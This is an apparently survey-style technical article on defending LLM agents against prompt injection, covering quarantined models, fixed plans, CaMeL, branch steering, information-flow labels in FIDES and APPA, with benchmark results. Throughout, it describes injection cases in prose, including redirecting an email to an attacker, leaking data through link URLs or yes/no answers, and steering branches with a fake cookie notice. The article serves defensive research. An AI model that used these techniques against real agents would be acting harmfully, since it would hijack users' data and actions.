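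Short text is harder to judge. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a coding assistant could read unfamiliar documentation through a quarantined model that returns only a formal description of the functions, with names of at most 30 characters. Willison doubts that this limit is short enough, since a function name can itself read like a command. FIDES's ordering would treat such a name as carrying far more information than a choice from a list, since 30 characters can carry about 141 bits even with only 26 letters.

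### Reading each document separately

If an agent gives ten documents to one quarantined model, the author of one document can influence what the model reports about the other nine. The map-reduce pattern prevents this. It is named after a distributed computing method in which many machines process separate pieces of data (map) and a final step combines their results (reduce).

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an agent that finds this month's invoices and emails them to the accounting department. The orchestrator starts a separate model for each file, and each model returns only whether its file is an invoice. The agent then collects the files classified as invoices, and another model writes and sends the email. An attacker can write a malicious file that is classified as an invoice, but could achieve the same by submitting a real-looking invoice. The malicious file cannot make the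 agent attach somebody's salary letter, as long as the model that writes the email does not read the text of the selected files.

The final step can also limit the effect of a false answer. In the shopping agent of Jacob and colleagues, the quarantined model reads each product review and scores how strongly it supports the product and how relevant it is. The agent uses the median of each score. If five reviews have support scores of 2, 3, 3, 4 and 5, the median is 3 and the mean is 3.4. If an injection changes the 2 to a 10, the median rises to 4 and the mean to 5. An attacker who writes most of the reviews can still set the median, just as they could with ordinary fake reviews.

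Map-reduce can score résumés separately to produce a shortlist, but it does not suit a detailed comparison of two candidates, which needs information from both résumés. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that the privileged model instead write a template with gaps for details such as the difference in years of experience. A program would then fill the gaps from separate readings of each résumé. A candidate can still trick the model that reads their résumé into reporting too many years of experience.

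### Removing text that has done its work

Variable passing hides tool results from the planner, but it does not hide an injection in the user's own message, such as one in pasted text. The agent has to read this message to learn what the user wants, so the orchestrator can only remove it from the context afterwards. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call this pattern context minimisation.

In one example, a customer tries to talk a car seller's chatbot into a large discount. The agent first translates the customer's message into a database query for current offers. The orchestrator then deletes the message, including the demand for a discount, from the context and gives the model only the query's results, from which it writes the quote. The customer could still influence the query, so it must be one that this customer may safely run.

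The deletion has to cover any text that could still contain the injection. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms, gets a diagnosis from a database or a doctor, and explains it in plain language. If the orchestrator removes the patient's message but keeps the summary, an injection can survive in the summary. If it removes both, the explanation can no longer refer to what the patient described. Restricting the summary to a schema with no free-text fields keeps most of the useful information, as long as the symptoms fit the available fields.

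### Valid answers can be wrong

A schema limits the form of an answer, but an attacker can often do harm within that form. Willison discusses an example in which a user asks an agent to send Bob a document that Bob requested, and both Bob's address and the document's name are in some meeting notes. The planner never receives the notes. It uses the quarantined model to extract the address, stores the result in a variable and passes the variable's name to the mail tool. If the notes contain an injection, the quarantined model can return the attacker's address instead. The document then goes to the attacker, even though the address is a valid email address and the sequence of calls is exactly what the user wanted.

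Dongol describes this case in a formal threat model. In the dual-LLM pattern, an injection can only corrupt an answer, but that answer may depend on everything in the query, including secrets. If an agent uses the user's recent mail to draft a reply to a stranger, the stranger's email may therefore influence a model that is also reading private messages. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that the draft could carry private data in invisible characters, or pass an injection on to the user's colleagues' assistants.

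Displaying the quarantined model's answer to the user also carries risks. The answer might include a link with private data encoded in its address, or an image that sends such data to the attacker's server when it loads. Willison recommends that assistants display links and images only from approved sites. Even then, the text could persuade the user to copy the data to the attacker's site.

Jacob and colleagues exclude misleading content from their threat model because it does not change the task the agent is carrying out. This is a reasonable way to define prompt injection, but misleading content can still cause an agent to send a document to the wrong person. To prevent that, the orchestrator has to check where the address came from before it sends the document.

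### Small answers add up

Suppose a planner inspects ten yes-or-no answers about untrusted emails instead of one. Each answer carries at most one bit, so together they can carry up to ten, enough to distinguish 2¹⁰ = 1,024 cases. If the planner's decisions allow that many paths, whoever wrote the emails may be able to steer the agent down any of them.

The type labels in FIDES do not track how many answers the planner has received. When the planner combines two pieces of data, the result takes the smallest type that covers both, and for two Booleans that is still a Boolean. The context therefore has the same label after ten answers as after one, so a policy that accepts the first answer also accepts the tenth. To limit the total, the orchestrator would need to count answers across the run, and across later runs if the attacker can send more emails.

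Yes-or-no answers can also leak secrets. If a query contains both an attacker's email and a secret four-digit code, the attacker can try to make the answer depend on the code. If the agent replies to the attacker only when the answer is yes, the presence or absence of a reply reveals one bit. Fourteen such answers are enough to identify any of the 10,000 possible codes, since 2¹⁴ is 16,384. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that their guarantee does not cover information revealed by which calls an agent makes. Keeping the code and the email in separate queries, as map-reduce would, prevents this leak.

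A count of bits also leaves out what each answer can make the agent do. Costa and colleagues suggest that a planner could choose between scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding an email. That choice carries less than two bits, yet it lets the sender of an untrusted email decide whether the agent forwards something. Ten answers that only sort messages into folders carry more information but could do much less damage.

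## Fixing the sequence of actions before untrusted data is read

Before an agent reads its first email or web page, its context holds only text supplied by the operator and the user. Unless the user has pasted in text from elsewhere, a plan made at this point cannot contain an attacker's instructions. If the orchestrator then refuses every action outside the plan, nothing the agent reads later can add an action.

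Security researchers call this property control-flow integrity. The term comes from conventional software, where it means that a program under attack still follows only the paths its code allows. For agents, *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster et al., 2026) defines it as requiring that every action at run time belong to a plan derived from the user's trusted request.

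### From a fixed menu to a program

In the strictest design, the action selector, developers write the list of permitted actions and the model only picks from it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of a customer service chatbot that can send a link to the customer's last order or point the customer to the settings page for passwords or payment details. The results of these actions never return to the model, so text in them cannot influence its choices. Developers can add some flexibility with templates, such as a database query with blanks for the model to fill in. But an assistant that sorts files by their contents would gain little from a language model under this design, because the developers would have to build the sorting into the actions.

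Plan-then-execute lets the model write a new list of actions for each request. To send today's schedule to the user's boss, John Doe, the plan needs two calls:

- calendar.read(today)
- email.write(____, "john.doe@company.com")

The blank stands for the message body, which the agent fills in after reading the calendar. If a calendar entry contains an instruction to delete tomorrow's meetings, the orchestrator blocks the deletion because it isn't in the plan. An instruction to send the schedule to someone else also fails, because the plan already specifies the recipient's address. The entry can still change what John Doe reads, for example by adding a false meeting or a request to approve a payment.

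The recipient is safe here only because the user named him. In another example from Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, the user asks the agent to tell their regular collaborators about a vacation. The agent has to work out who those collaborators are, perhaps from the frequency of recent emails, so an attacker who emails the user often enough might be included.

A plan that fixes only tool names protects even less. For example, a file assistant might commit to a command that finds files and another that moves them, but leave their arguments open. An injection could then make it find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

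The protection also depends on what carries out the plan. *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) describes executors that range from a simple program to a complete agent with its own loop. If a step says only "find a suitable hotel" and an agent works out how to do that from live web pages, an injection can redirect it within the step. The paper therefore recommends giving the executor only the tools for its current step. An agent adding up costs should have a calculator but no access to email, even if the next step is to email the total.

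In code-then-execute, the model writes a program instead of a list. For the calendar task, a program modelled on one by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues could look like this:

```
schedule = calendar.read(today)
message = reader_model("write this up as a short note", schedule)
email.write(message, "john.doe@company.com")
```

The second line passes the calendar to a model without tools, as in the dual-LLM pattern. A program can also contain loops and conditions. The vacation notice needs a loop because the planner does not know how many collaborators there are. The message body is no safer than before.

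### CaMeL

CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) implements code-then-execute. As *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) describes it, a trusted planner model receives the user's request and writes the complete program before the agent observes anything. An interpreter then runs the program, and a quarantined model processes untrusted content when the program calls for it.

The interpreter also limits which data may reach a tool. According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL tags each value with its origin and permitted readers, and checks the tags when the value reaches a tool call. If the quarantined model extracts an address from meeting notes, the tag records that origin, so a policy can block sending a document there even when the fixed sequence of calls includes the send.

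Narisetty and colleagues also cite CaMeL's reported results with OpenAI's o3 model. Under attack, CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, and no injection within its threat model succeeded. CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

CaMeL's drawbacks were larger with a weaker model. Li, Liu and colleagues (2025) ran it with GPT-4o-mini in *DRIFT*. Under attack, it completed 35.4% of tasks, compared with 48.3% for the undefended agent. In runs without attacks, it used about seven times as many tokens. Li and colleagues were comparing CaMeL with their own system, but the results are plausible because a weaker model would probably struggle to write the whole program without seeing any data.

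Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026) point out in *Architecting Secure AI Agents* that an outdated function or a missing software package can stop a fixed plan even when nobody is attacking it.

### Tasks that no fixed plan can complete

For other tasks, no fixed sequence of calls would work, even if every tool ran perfectly. Costa and colleagues call these tasks data dependent, and call a task data independent if a single sequence of calls solves it in every starting state.

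Their request to complete the tasks due today in a to-do app is one of them. Suppose that in state d₁ the only entry is "send Ana the budget", and in state d₂ it is "cancel Thursday's dentist appointment". In d₁, a successful run reads the list and sends a file. In d₂, it reads the list and deletes a calendar event. No sequence solves both, so

⟦t⟧(d₁) ∩ ⟦t⟧(d₂) = ∅

A program with conditions would not solve the general problem either, because it would need a branch for every task that anyone might write down. The entries are instructions that the user wants the agent to follow. If other people can add to the list, an attacker's instruction looks like any other entry.

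Costa and colleagues classified the AgentDojo tasks by hand and found that only 5% of office tasks and 10% of travel tasks were data dependent, compared with 43.8% of banking tasks and 42.9% of Slack tasks. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

Xiang and colleagues cite a much lower count, with only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks requiring the agent to change its plan or policy during the run. The two counts probably differ because some data-dependent tasks need only a simple branch, such as creating a calendar event if an email requests a meeting.

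### Writing the branches in advance

If the planner can foresee what the agent might find, it can write a branch for each case. *Web Agents Should Adopt the Compile-and-Execute Paradigm* (Piet, Chow and colleagues, 2026) proposes this for agents that use websites. Page content can supply values and determine which branch the program takes, but it cannot add an action. A dishonest seller might still trick the agent into buying a counterfeit of the watch the user wanted, but could not make it access the user's bank account.

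Piet and colleagues examined the tasks in WebArena, a benchmark that uses self-hosted shops, forums and other sites. They judged all the tasks compatible with the design, and 81% needed no language model once the program was running. These figures come from an analysis of the tasks, not from a working agent. They also assume that each site offers a trusted and complete set of functions, such as one for reading reviews and another for adding an item to the cart, but most sites lack such a set.

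Without such functions, the agent has to click and type. A click at the same coordinates might open a product page, submit an order or delete an item, and a planner cannot predict which without access to the page. These functions may also make agents more capable. *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (2026) cites results on WebArena in which agents that could call a site's functions outperformed agents that only read a description of the page's elements.

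Foerster and colleagues planned individual clicks for agents that operate a whole computer. Their planner writes a program with branches for cookie notices, browsers that are already open and clicks that fail. Before an action, a quarantined vision model describes the screen. A second query checks that description against a condition from the plan, such as whether a cookie notice is visible, and the interpreter follows the branch that matches the yes or no answer.

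The programs averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 and 4 for CaMeL's programs on AgentDojo. Roughly half of the steps were fallbacks that a given run never used. Planning everything at once used fewer tokens than querying the planner again at every step, as FIDES does. The CaMeL version used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent, while a version based on FIDES used 29.6 times as many.

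Foerster and colleagues report that the design kept up to 57% of a frontier model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary desktop software. That figure counts a task as solved if any of five attempts succeeds. With one attempt, the design kept 28%. The lower figure is more relevant to payments and messages, which an agent cannot safely repeat until one attempt works.

### What branches give back to the attacker

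When a program branches on page content, whoever wrote that content can influence which branch the program takes. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In one test, an advertisement that imitated a cookie notice got the agent to click through to a site the attacker controlled. The program already contained a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the click was part of the plan. Foerster and colleagues checked the vision model's answers against the page's code and against a second model, but neither check reliably stopped their attacks.

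Zingrillo and colleagues built a benchmark of 101 such tasks, from bank transfers to changes in medication doses. On the tasks that ordinary agents could attempt, steering succeeded 94.4% of the time against a standard agent and 89.5% against one with a fixed branching plan, so the plan alone gave little protection against steering.

COBRA adds limits to each branch before the agent sees any page. The planner specifies which sites and tools the branch may use and which values it may send. The agent's web requests pass through a proxy, which blocks any request outside those limits. The proxy checks requests rather than clicks because a click alone does not show what operation it will cause. COBRA blocked every attack in the benchmark and kept 97% of the utility of the version without limits.

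The benchmark counts an attack as successful only if the harmful action violates the limits in force at that moment. The result of zero successful attacks therefore mainly confirms that COBRA enforces its limits. An attacker can still choose between branches that comply with them. Without an approved description of a site's operations, COBRA's proxy can restrict only which sites the agent contacts, so it cannot tell a harmless request to the user's bank from a money transfer.

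For the to-do list, a planner could prepare branches for sending a file, booking a meeting and paying a bill. Anyone who can add an entry to the list could then trigger any of these actions, within the limits the planner had set.

### Replanning under constraints

A planner cannot always foresee every action a task will need. Xiang and colleagues give the example of debugging, where nobody knows in advance which files the agent will have to read, change or run. They conclude that complex tasks often require the agent to revise its plan as it works. The revision depends on what the agent has found, so untrusted content can influence the new plan.

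DRIFT, the system by Li and colleagues, allows revisions but treats them differently according to the harm they could do. It works in three stages:

- Before the agent reads any data, a planner model turns the user's request into a minimal sequence of tool calls and a checklist for their arguments. If the user asked for a flight from Paris to London, the checklist catches an injection that changes the route to London to New York, even though the tool is the same.
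- When the agent requests a call outside the plan, a validator model classifies it as read, write or execute. DRIFT approves reads automatically. For the other two, the validator judges whether the call fits the user's intent. If it does, DRIFT adds the call to the plan, and if not, it asks the user.
- After each call, an isolator model looks for instructions in the result that conflict with the user's request, and ordinary software masks them before the result enters the agent's memory.

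Li and colleagues added these parts one at a time to an agent based on GPT-4o-mini and tested each version on AgentDojo.

| Version | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 63.6% | 48.3% | 30.7% |
| Fixed plan | 43.2% | 36.2% | 2.1% |
| Plan and validator | 58.5% | 45.8% | 5.4% |
| Plan, validator and isolator | 57.3% | 50.9% | 1.4% |

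The fixed plan stopped most attacks, but the agent failed about a third of the tasks it could otherwise complete. These failures were concentrated in longer tasks, with success falling sharply once a task needed three or more calls. Allowing revisions to the plan let the agent complete most of the lost tasks again, but more than doubled the attack success rate. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, CaMeL completed none.

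The isolator brought attack success back down, but it is an in-band defence because it is a language model that reads text the attacker wrote. Li and colleagues tested two attacks on it, one written by hand and one optimised automatically on a sample of cases, and each raised attack success only to about 2%. Both tests were much smaller than the searches and competition that Nasr and colleagues used, and Xiang and colleagues expect that adaptive attackers could still mislead DRIFT's models.

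Automatically approving reads also creates a privacy risk, although Li and colleagues treat reading as harmless because it changes nothing. In an attack that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe, an injection in an outsider's email makes the assistant search for private information, which then leaks in the reply the user requested.

Xiang and colleagues accept that some revisions need a model's judgement, but want to restrict what that model receives. It would get a narrow, structured input, such as the proposed change to the plan, and answer one limited question about it without reading the web page or error message that prompted the change. They present this as a direction for research. The design reduces the attacker's influence but doesn't remove it, because a structured proposal can still contain values the attacker chose, such as the name of a malicious software package.

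Other systems check calls against the plan. In *PlanGuard* (2026), a separate planner receives only the user's request and the tool definitions, and lists the actions it expects. Software allows actions that exactly match the list and checks the others further. In *ActGuard* (2026), a complete plan is considered too hard to predict, so the agent predicts only which tools it might plausibly use next. If it calls a different tool, the system interprets the deviation rather than automatically forbidding the call. This adapts easily to new information, but the agent reads the history so far before making each prediction, so an injection already in that history could influence both the prediction and the call.

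### Asking the user

It is safest for an agent to question the user before it reads anything untrusted, because an attacker has had no chance to influence the question. If a task requires a security-critical value, such as an account number, and neither the request nor a source authorised by the plan can supply it, COBRA asks the user for it during planning. COBRA treats the answer as trusted for that request only.

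The user could also approve the whole plan at this point. Del Rosario and colleagues recommend that a person or a separate program inspect a plan before it runs. Checking the two-line calendar plan is easy, but few users would check a program with 40 branches.

Users find it harder to answer questions well during the run. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that reviewing an email takes little effort in a desktop application but can be much harder through a voice interface. The attacker may also have written the text that the user has to judge. Xiang and colleagues consider a coding agent that finds instructions to install a malicious package that appears relevant. People often follow such instructions without checking them.

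Some questions still need a person to answer them. If a user asks for a summary of all urgent emails, even a perfect model cannot know which ones that user considers urgent. For the to-do list, the agent could show the user today's entries and make a separate plan for each one the user selects. The agent would then act on an attacker's entry only if the user selected it. The user might notice a task they never wrote, though this is less likely if colleagues regularly add tasks to the same list.

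## Labelling data and tracking it through a run

A fixed plan determines which tools an agent calls, but not where the data in those calls came from or who may receive it. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) gives the example of an agent that needs a secret key to upload software to a server. Access control can only grant or deny the agent access to the key. The operator wants a narrower rule that lets the agent send the key only to that server.

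Information-flow control can express such a rule. Microsoft's *information flow control moving toward secure autonomous agents* breaks it into three steps: labelling all data the agent takes in, labelling derived data according to its sources, and checking the labels before acting. Security researchers call this taint tracking when the software carries the labels as it runs.

### Labels and how they combine

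The simplest labels are T (trusted) and U (untrusted) for integrity, and L ("low", or public) and H ("high", or secret) for confidentiality. The orders T ⊑ U and L ⊑ H put the more restrictive label on the right, and data may flow from left to right but not back. The join of two labels, written ⊔, is the least restrictive label that covers both, so T ⊔ U = U. A set of labels with such an order and join forms a lattice, or strictly a join-semilattice.

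The label H does not specify who may read the data. In the readers lattice that Costa and colleagues use, each label is the set of people with permission. If A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another, only people with access to both may read a text derived from both:

{A, B, C} ⊔ {B, C, D} = {A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Integrity labels can also be sets of possible writers. Their join is the union, because any of A, B, C and D could have contributed to the combined text. A full label is a pair such as (U, {B, C}), and joins apply to each half separately.

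*SPA* traces the confidentiality half to the Bell–LaPadula model and the integrity half to the Biba model, both from classical computer security. Narisetty and colleagues apply Biba's rules to agents by lowering a model's integrity level to that of any untrusted data it reads. The model is then not allowed to authorise an action that requires a higher level.

### How FIDES carries labels through the loop

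FIDES, the planner by Costa and colleagues, adds labels to the ordinary agent loop:

1. The system message and the user's request start as trusted and public, unless the operator chooses otherwise. Tools attach labels to their results, either one for the whole result or one for each field.
2. When the planner queries the model, the answer receives the join of the labels of all messages in the history and of the tool definitions.
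3. If the model requests a tool call, the loop checks it against the policy, using one label for the call itself and one for each argument. The tool runs only if the call passes.
4. The tool's result receives the join of the call's label, the arguments' labels and the labels of any stored data the tool read. Anything the tool writes receives the same label, so a note saved after reading an untrusted email is still untrusted when the agent opens it later.

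In the Project X task, suppose that the user, the manager and a colleague called Ana may read the genuine project emails, which the operator trusts. The operator treats mail from outside the company as untrusted and public. Once the basic planner has put all the emails into the context, the context's label is

(T, everyone) ⊔ (T, {user, manager, Ana}) ⊔ (U, everyone) = (U, {user, manager, Ana})

The model may have ignored the attacker's email completely, but the orchestrator cannot tell, so it treats the next answer as untrusted.

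### Two policies applied to the email task

Costa and colleagues define an integrity policy for consequential actions. It permits a call with n arguments only if

ℓ(call) ⊔ ℓ(arg₁) ⊔ … ⊔ ℓ(argₙ) = (T, _)

where ℓ is the label of an item and the underscore stands for any set of readers. Their confidentiality policy applies to each argument that a tool sends out. If R is the set of people who will receive the argument and its label is (_, S), the policy requires

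S ⊑ R, which in the readers lattice means R ⊆ S

Every recipient must therefore already have permission to read the data. The table shows how the policies apply to four calls. The first three come after the basic planner has read the emails. In the fourth, the agent has read only a trusted internal budget, which the user asks it to send to an outside accountant.

| Requested call | Integrity policy | Confidentiality policy | Both together |
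|---|---|---|---|
| Send the summary to the manager | Blocks | Allows | Block |
| Send the top email to the attacker | Blocks | Blocks | Block |
| Send Ana a false deadline that the attacker wrote | Blocks | Allows | Block |
| Send the budget to the accountant | Allows | Blocks | Block |

The confidentiality policy alone still lets the attacker mislead Ana. The integrity policy alone stops every injection in the table, but it allows the budget to leave the company because the decision to send it came from a trusted context and was presumably intentional. Costa and colleagues relate this to robust declassification, the principle that an attacker must not be able to influence the release of secrets. Together, the two policies block both of the user's legitimate requests.

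The integrity policy as written blocks the call that sends the summary to the manager, even if a quarantined model writes the summary, because the summary is an untrusted argument. In their experiments, Costa and colleagues checked only the call's label, which lets the summary through but leaves the recipient's address unprotected. They suggest a better rule for messages, which requires a trusted call and a trusted recipient but allows an untrusted body.

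The result also depends on how the operator labels the attacker's email. Costa and colleagues infer an email's readers from its sender and recipients, so only the attacker and the user may read the attacker's email. Joining its label with those of the project emails leaves the user as the only permitted reader, and the confidentiality policy then blocks the summary to the manager. An outsider could stop the task just by sending an email that the agent includes.

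### Explicit and implicit flows

These checks control explicit flows, in which a call carries the protected data. An implicit flow reveals information through the agent's choice of action. Suppose an agent stores two public web pages, A and B, under variable names and then reads the user's confidential salary letter. The agent publishes page A if the letter announces a pay rise and page B otherwise. Both pages are public, so either call satisfies the confidentiality policy. But anyone who knows the agent's rule and sees page A published can infer the pay rise.

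FIDES guarantees a property called explicit secrecy. To define it, Costa and colleagues treat two states of the stored data, d₁ and d₂, as equivalent if all their public parts match, written d₁ =_L d₂. Each sequence of steps that the agent might take has an effect g on the data. Explicit secrecy requires that, for every such sequence,

if d₁ =_L d₂, then g(d₁) =_L g(d₂)

In the example, the letter in d₁ includes a pay rise and the letter in d₂ does not. The sequence that publishes page A has the same public effect in both states, and so does the sequence that publishes page B. The agent therefore satisfies explicit secrecy, even though the letter determines which sequence it follows.

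Noninterference is stronger because it covers that choice. If F(d) is the state after the agent's complete run from d, noninterference requires that

if d₁ =_L d₂, then F(d₁) =_L F(d₂)

The example violates this, because one run publishes page A and the other publishes page B.

A system can catch some implicit flows by giving each branch of a program the label of the condition that selected it. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which defines a formal language for agents, joins the current branch's label to results computed inside it. In the salary letter example, this would mark the publishing call as secret whichever page it used. But the agent could also reveal the pay rise by publishing nothing. Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference would in effect forbid any publicly visible call after any call that might have read a secret. They consider this too restrictive and note that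 web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracking system for smartphones, accept the weaker guarantee.

The guarantee also doesn't cover leaks through timing or the size of network packets, and its proof assumes that the model always gives the same answer to the same input. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL's designers demonstrated two side channels in their own system, one through an indirect dependency and one through an error that the attacker triggers.

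### When one untrusted read blocks the rest of the run

An answer that inherits every label in the context often gets a stricter label than it needs, which is called over-tainting. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* describes this as unavoidable for now, because nobody can calculate precisely which inputs a model's answer depends on. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes the extreme case, label explosion, in which every item carries every label and the labels no longer distinguish one item from another.

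*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) proves that reading more data can never lift a block of this kind, because each new item either leaves the context's label unchanged or makes it stricter. With five possible readers and two levels of trust, the label can tighten at most 5 + 2 − 1 = 6 times, after which the data is untrusted and nobody may receive it. In one of the paper's test tasks, an agent confirms that an employee's personnel record exists and later tries to send a routine notice to the whole company. The record's label blocks the notice, even though the notice contains nothing from the record.

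Costa and colleagues measured the effect on task completion using AgentDojo. They ran each user task without an attack and with every injection task in the same environment. The attacker knew the names of the available tools. Most calls, such as payments, had to be trusted. Tools that send messages could also run in an untrusted context if the recipients were entitled to the content and the content had no untrusted link. The table gives the share of tasks completed when there was no attack, averaged over five runs.

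| Model and planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| GPT-4o, basic, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |
| o1, basic, no checks | 70.0% | 82.0% | 96.2% | 87.6% |
| o1, basic, with checks | 48.0% | 75.0% | 37.5% | 17.1% |
| o1, FIDES, with checks | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% |

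When both planners enforced the policies, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic planner with GPT-4o and 16 points more with o1, averaged over the four environments. With o1, FIDES still completed about 23 points fewer than the basic planner without enforcement. Many of the failures were intended, as in banking, where reading a file of instructions often blocked the payment. Others came from poor planning. In one Slack task, the agent listed all channels although the user had already named the right one, and the list made its context untrusted.

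With GPT-4o and no checks, 152 injections succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, Costa and colleagues counted no successful injections against either planner. They excluded cases that the benchmark had misjudged, actions that the policies permitted and injections that changed only the wording of an answer. This is weaker evidence than it appears, because the labels were based on the benchmark's attacks. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one injection task used it, so no attack could arrive through a field labelled as trusted. An operator has to label fields without a list of the attacks that will be tried.

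Both models are also old. Kravchenko and colleagues found that GPT-5.6 Luna, without any defence, followed none of AgentDojo's injections in 160 runs of workspace tasks, compared with 31% for GPT-4o. Newer models would probably also complete more tasks under FIDES, but better planning cannot help where the policy forbids a call that the task requires.

### Tracking influence more precisely

If the orchestrator could identify which messages influenced an answer, it could ignore the labels of the rest. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and colleagues that looks for a subset of the context that produces a similar answer. The model then answers again from that subset alone, so the new answer needs only that subset's labels. For example, if a question about office opening hours follows an untrusted email, the model could answer without the email and the result could stay trusted.

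RTBAS, another system that Costa and colleagues discuss, estimates influence from the model's attention or asks a language model to judge it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes replacing fixed labels with estimates of how much information an output carries about each input. An operator would need to decide how much influence is acceptable, and an attacker might try to keep the estimate below that level. Answering again from a smaller context avoids this risk because the model no longer receives the excluded text, but untrusted text could still affect the answer by influencing which text is kept.

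A source's influence can be hard to detect in the output. Cai and Wen (2026) argue in *Ghost in the Agent* that tracking has to cover copied text, reworded text, effects on the agent's decisions and information that persists in its memory. In 400 scenarios drawn from 20 agent frameworks, their tool, NeuroTaint, detected more flows from sources to sensitive actions than a baseline modelled on FIDES did. It analyses runs offline, so it is useful for audits but cannot stop a call.

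### Declassification and endorsement

Operators can also make exceptions. Declassification permits a specific release of secret data, such as telling a customer whether an order has shipped without showing the full record. Endorsement lets an agent treat selected untrusted data as trusted for a defined purpose. FIDES's exception for Booleans is a limited form of both. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) uses a separate checker to decide whether to declassify records for unknown recipients.

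An exception that changes one half of a label, either secrecy or trust, should not change the other. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, endorsing a secret password marks it as trusted but does not make it public. Endorsement also has no effect inside a branch chosen based on an untrusted value. Otherwise, an attacker who could steer the program into that branch could make their own text trusted.

Someone still has to decide which data deserves an exception. Costa and colleagues mention upgrading a document from untrusted to trusted after an injection detector finds nothing in it, but warn that relying on such detectors can weaken the guarantee. If the detector misses an injection, the document is labelled trusted and every later check accepts that label.

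The user can also decide, as in the planner by Kolluri and colleagues, but an attacker can target the user's judgement too. Narisetty and colleagues think the deepest open problem for these defences is tasks in which untrusted content has to trigger an action, such as adding a meeting to a calendar from an email.

### Recovering from a blocked call

Kravchenko and colleagues designed APPA to give an agent ways to continue after a refusal. It checks each call twice. Before the call, it computes the label the context would have afterwards, using the label that the tool declares for its output. This matters for a tool that reads and sends in one step. In one test, a tool fetches a confidential legal packet and emails it to an outside lawyer. The context is still open to internal and external readers, so a monitor that checked only the current label would allow the call. APPA first combines the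 two labels:

{internal, external} ∩ {internal} = {internal}

The lawyer is external, so APPA blocks the call before the tool reads or sends anything. APPA runs its other check after a tool has run and before the result enters the context, because the result may not match the tool's declaration.

When APPA refuses a call, it lists the available ways forward:

- Complete a missing step, such as recording legal clearance before sending contract terms.
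- Obtain approval for this exact call from a registered authority, which can be a person, a fixed rule or another model. The approval does not carry over to later calls.
- Replace the data with the output of a registered transformation, such as one that redacts personal details.
- Read the data in a child branch.

A child branch is a temporary copy of the agent. It starts with the parent's context and label, so the agent cannot shed restrictions by creating one. Whatever the child reads tightens only the child's label. For example, a support agent may need to read a public issue tracker and then update internal databases. A child reads the tracker and returns a ticket number, a severity and a component in a fixed schema. If the operator has decided to accept such answers as trusted, the parent keeps its label and can make the update. As with a quarantined model, an attacker may still cause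 the child to return a false severity. Discarding the child removes its text from the context but does not undo actions it took, such as sending an email.

Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA in 6,600 episodes with GPT-5.6 Luna, DeepSeek V4 Flash and Gemini 3.7 Flash. They compared five configurations, including unprotected agents and two setups of Microsoft's FIDES software. With each model, they ran each configuration five times per task with ordinary system prompts and five times with prompts that encouraged the agent to follow embedded instructions. They used 24 tasks from AgentThreatBench, for 3,600 episodes, and 20 office workflows from their own benchmark, Bench-Corp, for the other 3,000.

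APPA with enforcement ran in 1,320 of these episodes, and no attack succeeded. Across models and prompts, it completed 64.2% to 76.7% of tasks on AgentThreatBench and 87% to 91% on Bench-Corp. The attacks did work on unprotected agents, for example in 30.0% to 39.5% of Bench-Corp episodes when Kravchenko and colleagues switched enforcement off.

Much of APPA's utility came from its recovery mechanisms. On Bench-Corp, GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88.0% of tasks with full APPA, 56.5% without child branches and 35.0% without the recovery plans. No attack succeeded in any of these versions.

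The comparison with FIDES is less informative. On Bench-Corp, the FIDES setups completed 36% to 46% of tasks, and attacks succeeded in 26% to 35% of episodes. But Kravchenko and colleagues wrote the FIDES policies themselves and left out several rules that Bench-Corp tests, such as the order of required steps. They also designed Bench-Corp and APPA together. The 1,320 protected episodes repeat only 44 tasks, so they provide less evidence about unfamiliar attacks than their number suggests.

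### Who assigns the first labels

These guarantees assume that the initial labels are correct. Some labels can come from existing metadata, such as an email's recipients, although Costa and colleagues note that someone may have shared the email more widely since. Others depend on the tool's developer. In an example from Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026), a tool fetches bug reports from GitHub. It marks every report as untrusted, because outsiders can write them, and as private if the project is private. The label covers the whole report, so the agent cannot trust the genuine description without also trusting any instruction hidden below it.

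Developers will forget to label some tools, and sources disagree about how FIDES, as shipped in Microsoft's Agent Framework, treats the output of those tools. The May 2026 post warns that it treats the output as trusted and public. Microsoft's product documentation gives the default as untrusted and public, and describes this as failing closed. The documented default fails closed only for integrity. If a developer forgets to label a tool that looks up salaries, its results cannot drive a tool that refuses untrusted input, but a tool that publishes comments and checks only confidentiality would accept them. Operators should therefore test which default their installed version uses, and set a stricter confidentiality default if most of their tools return internal data.

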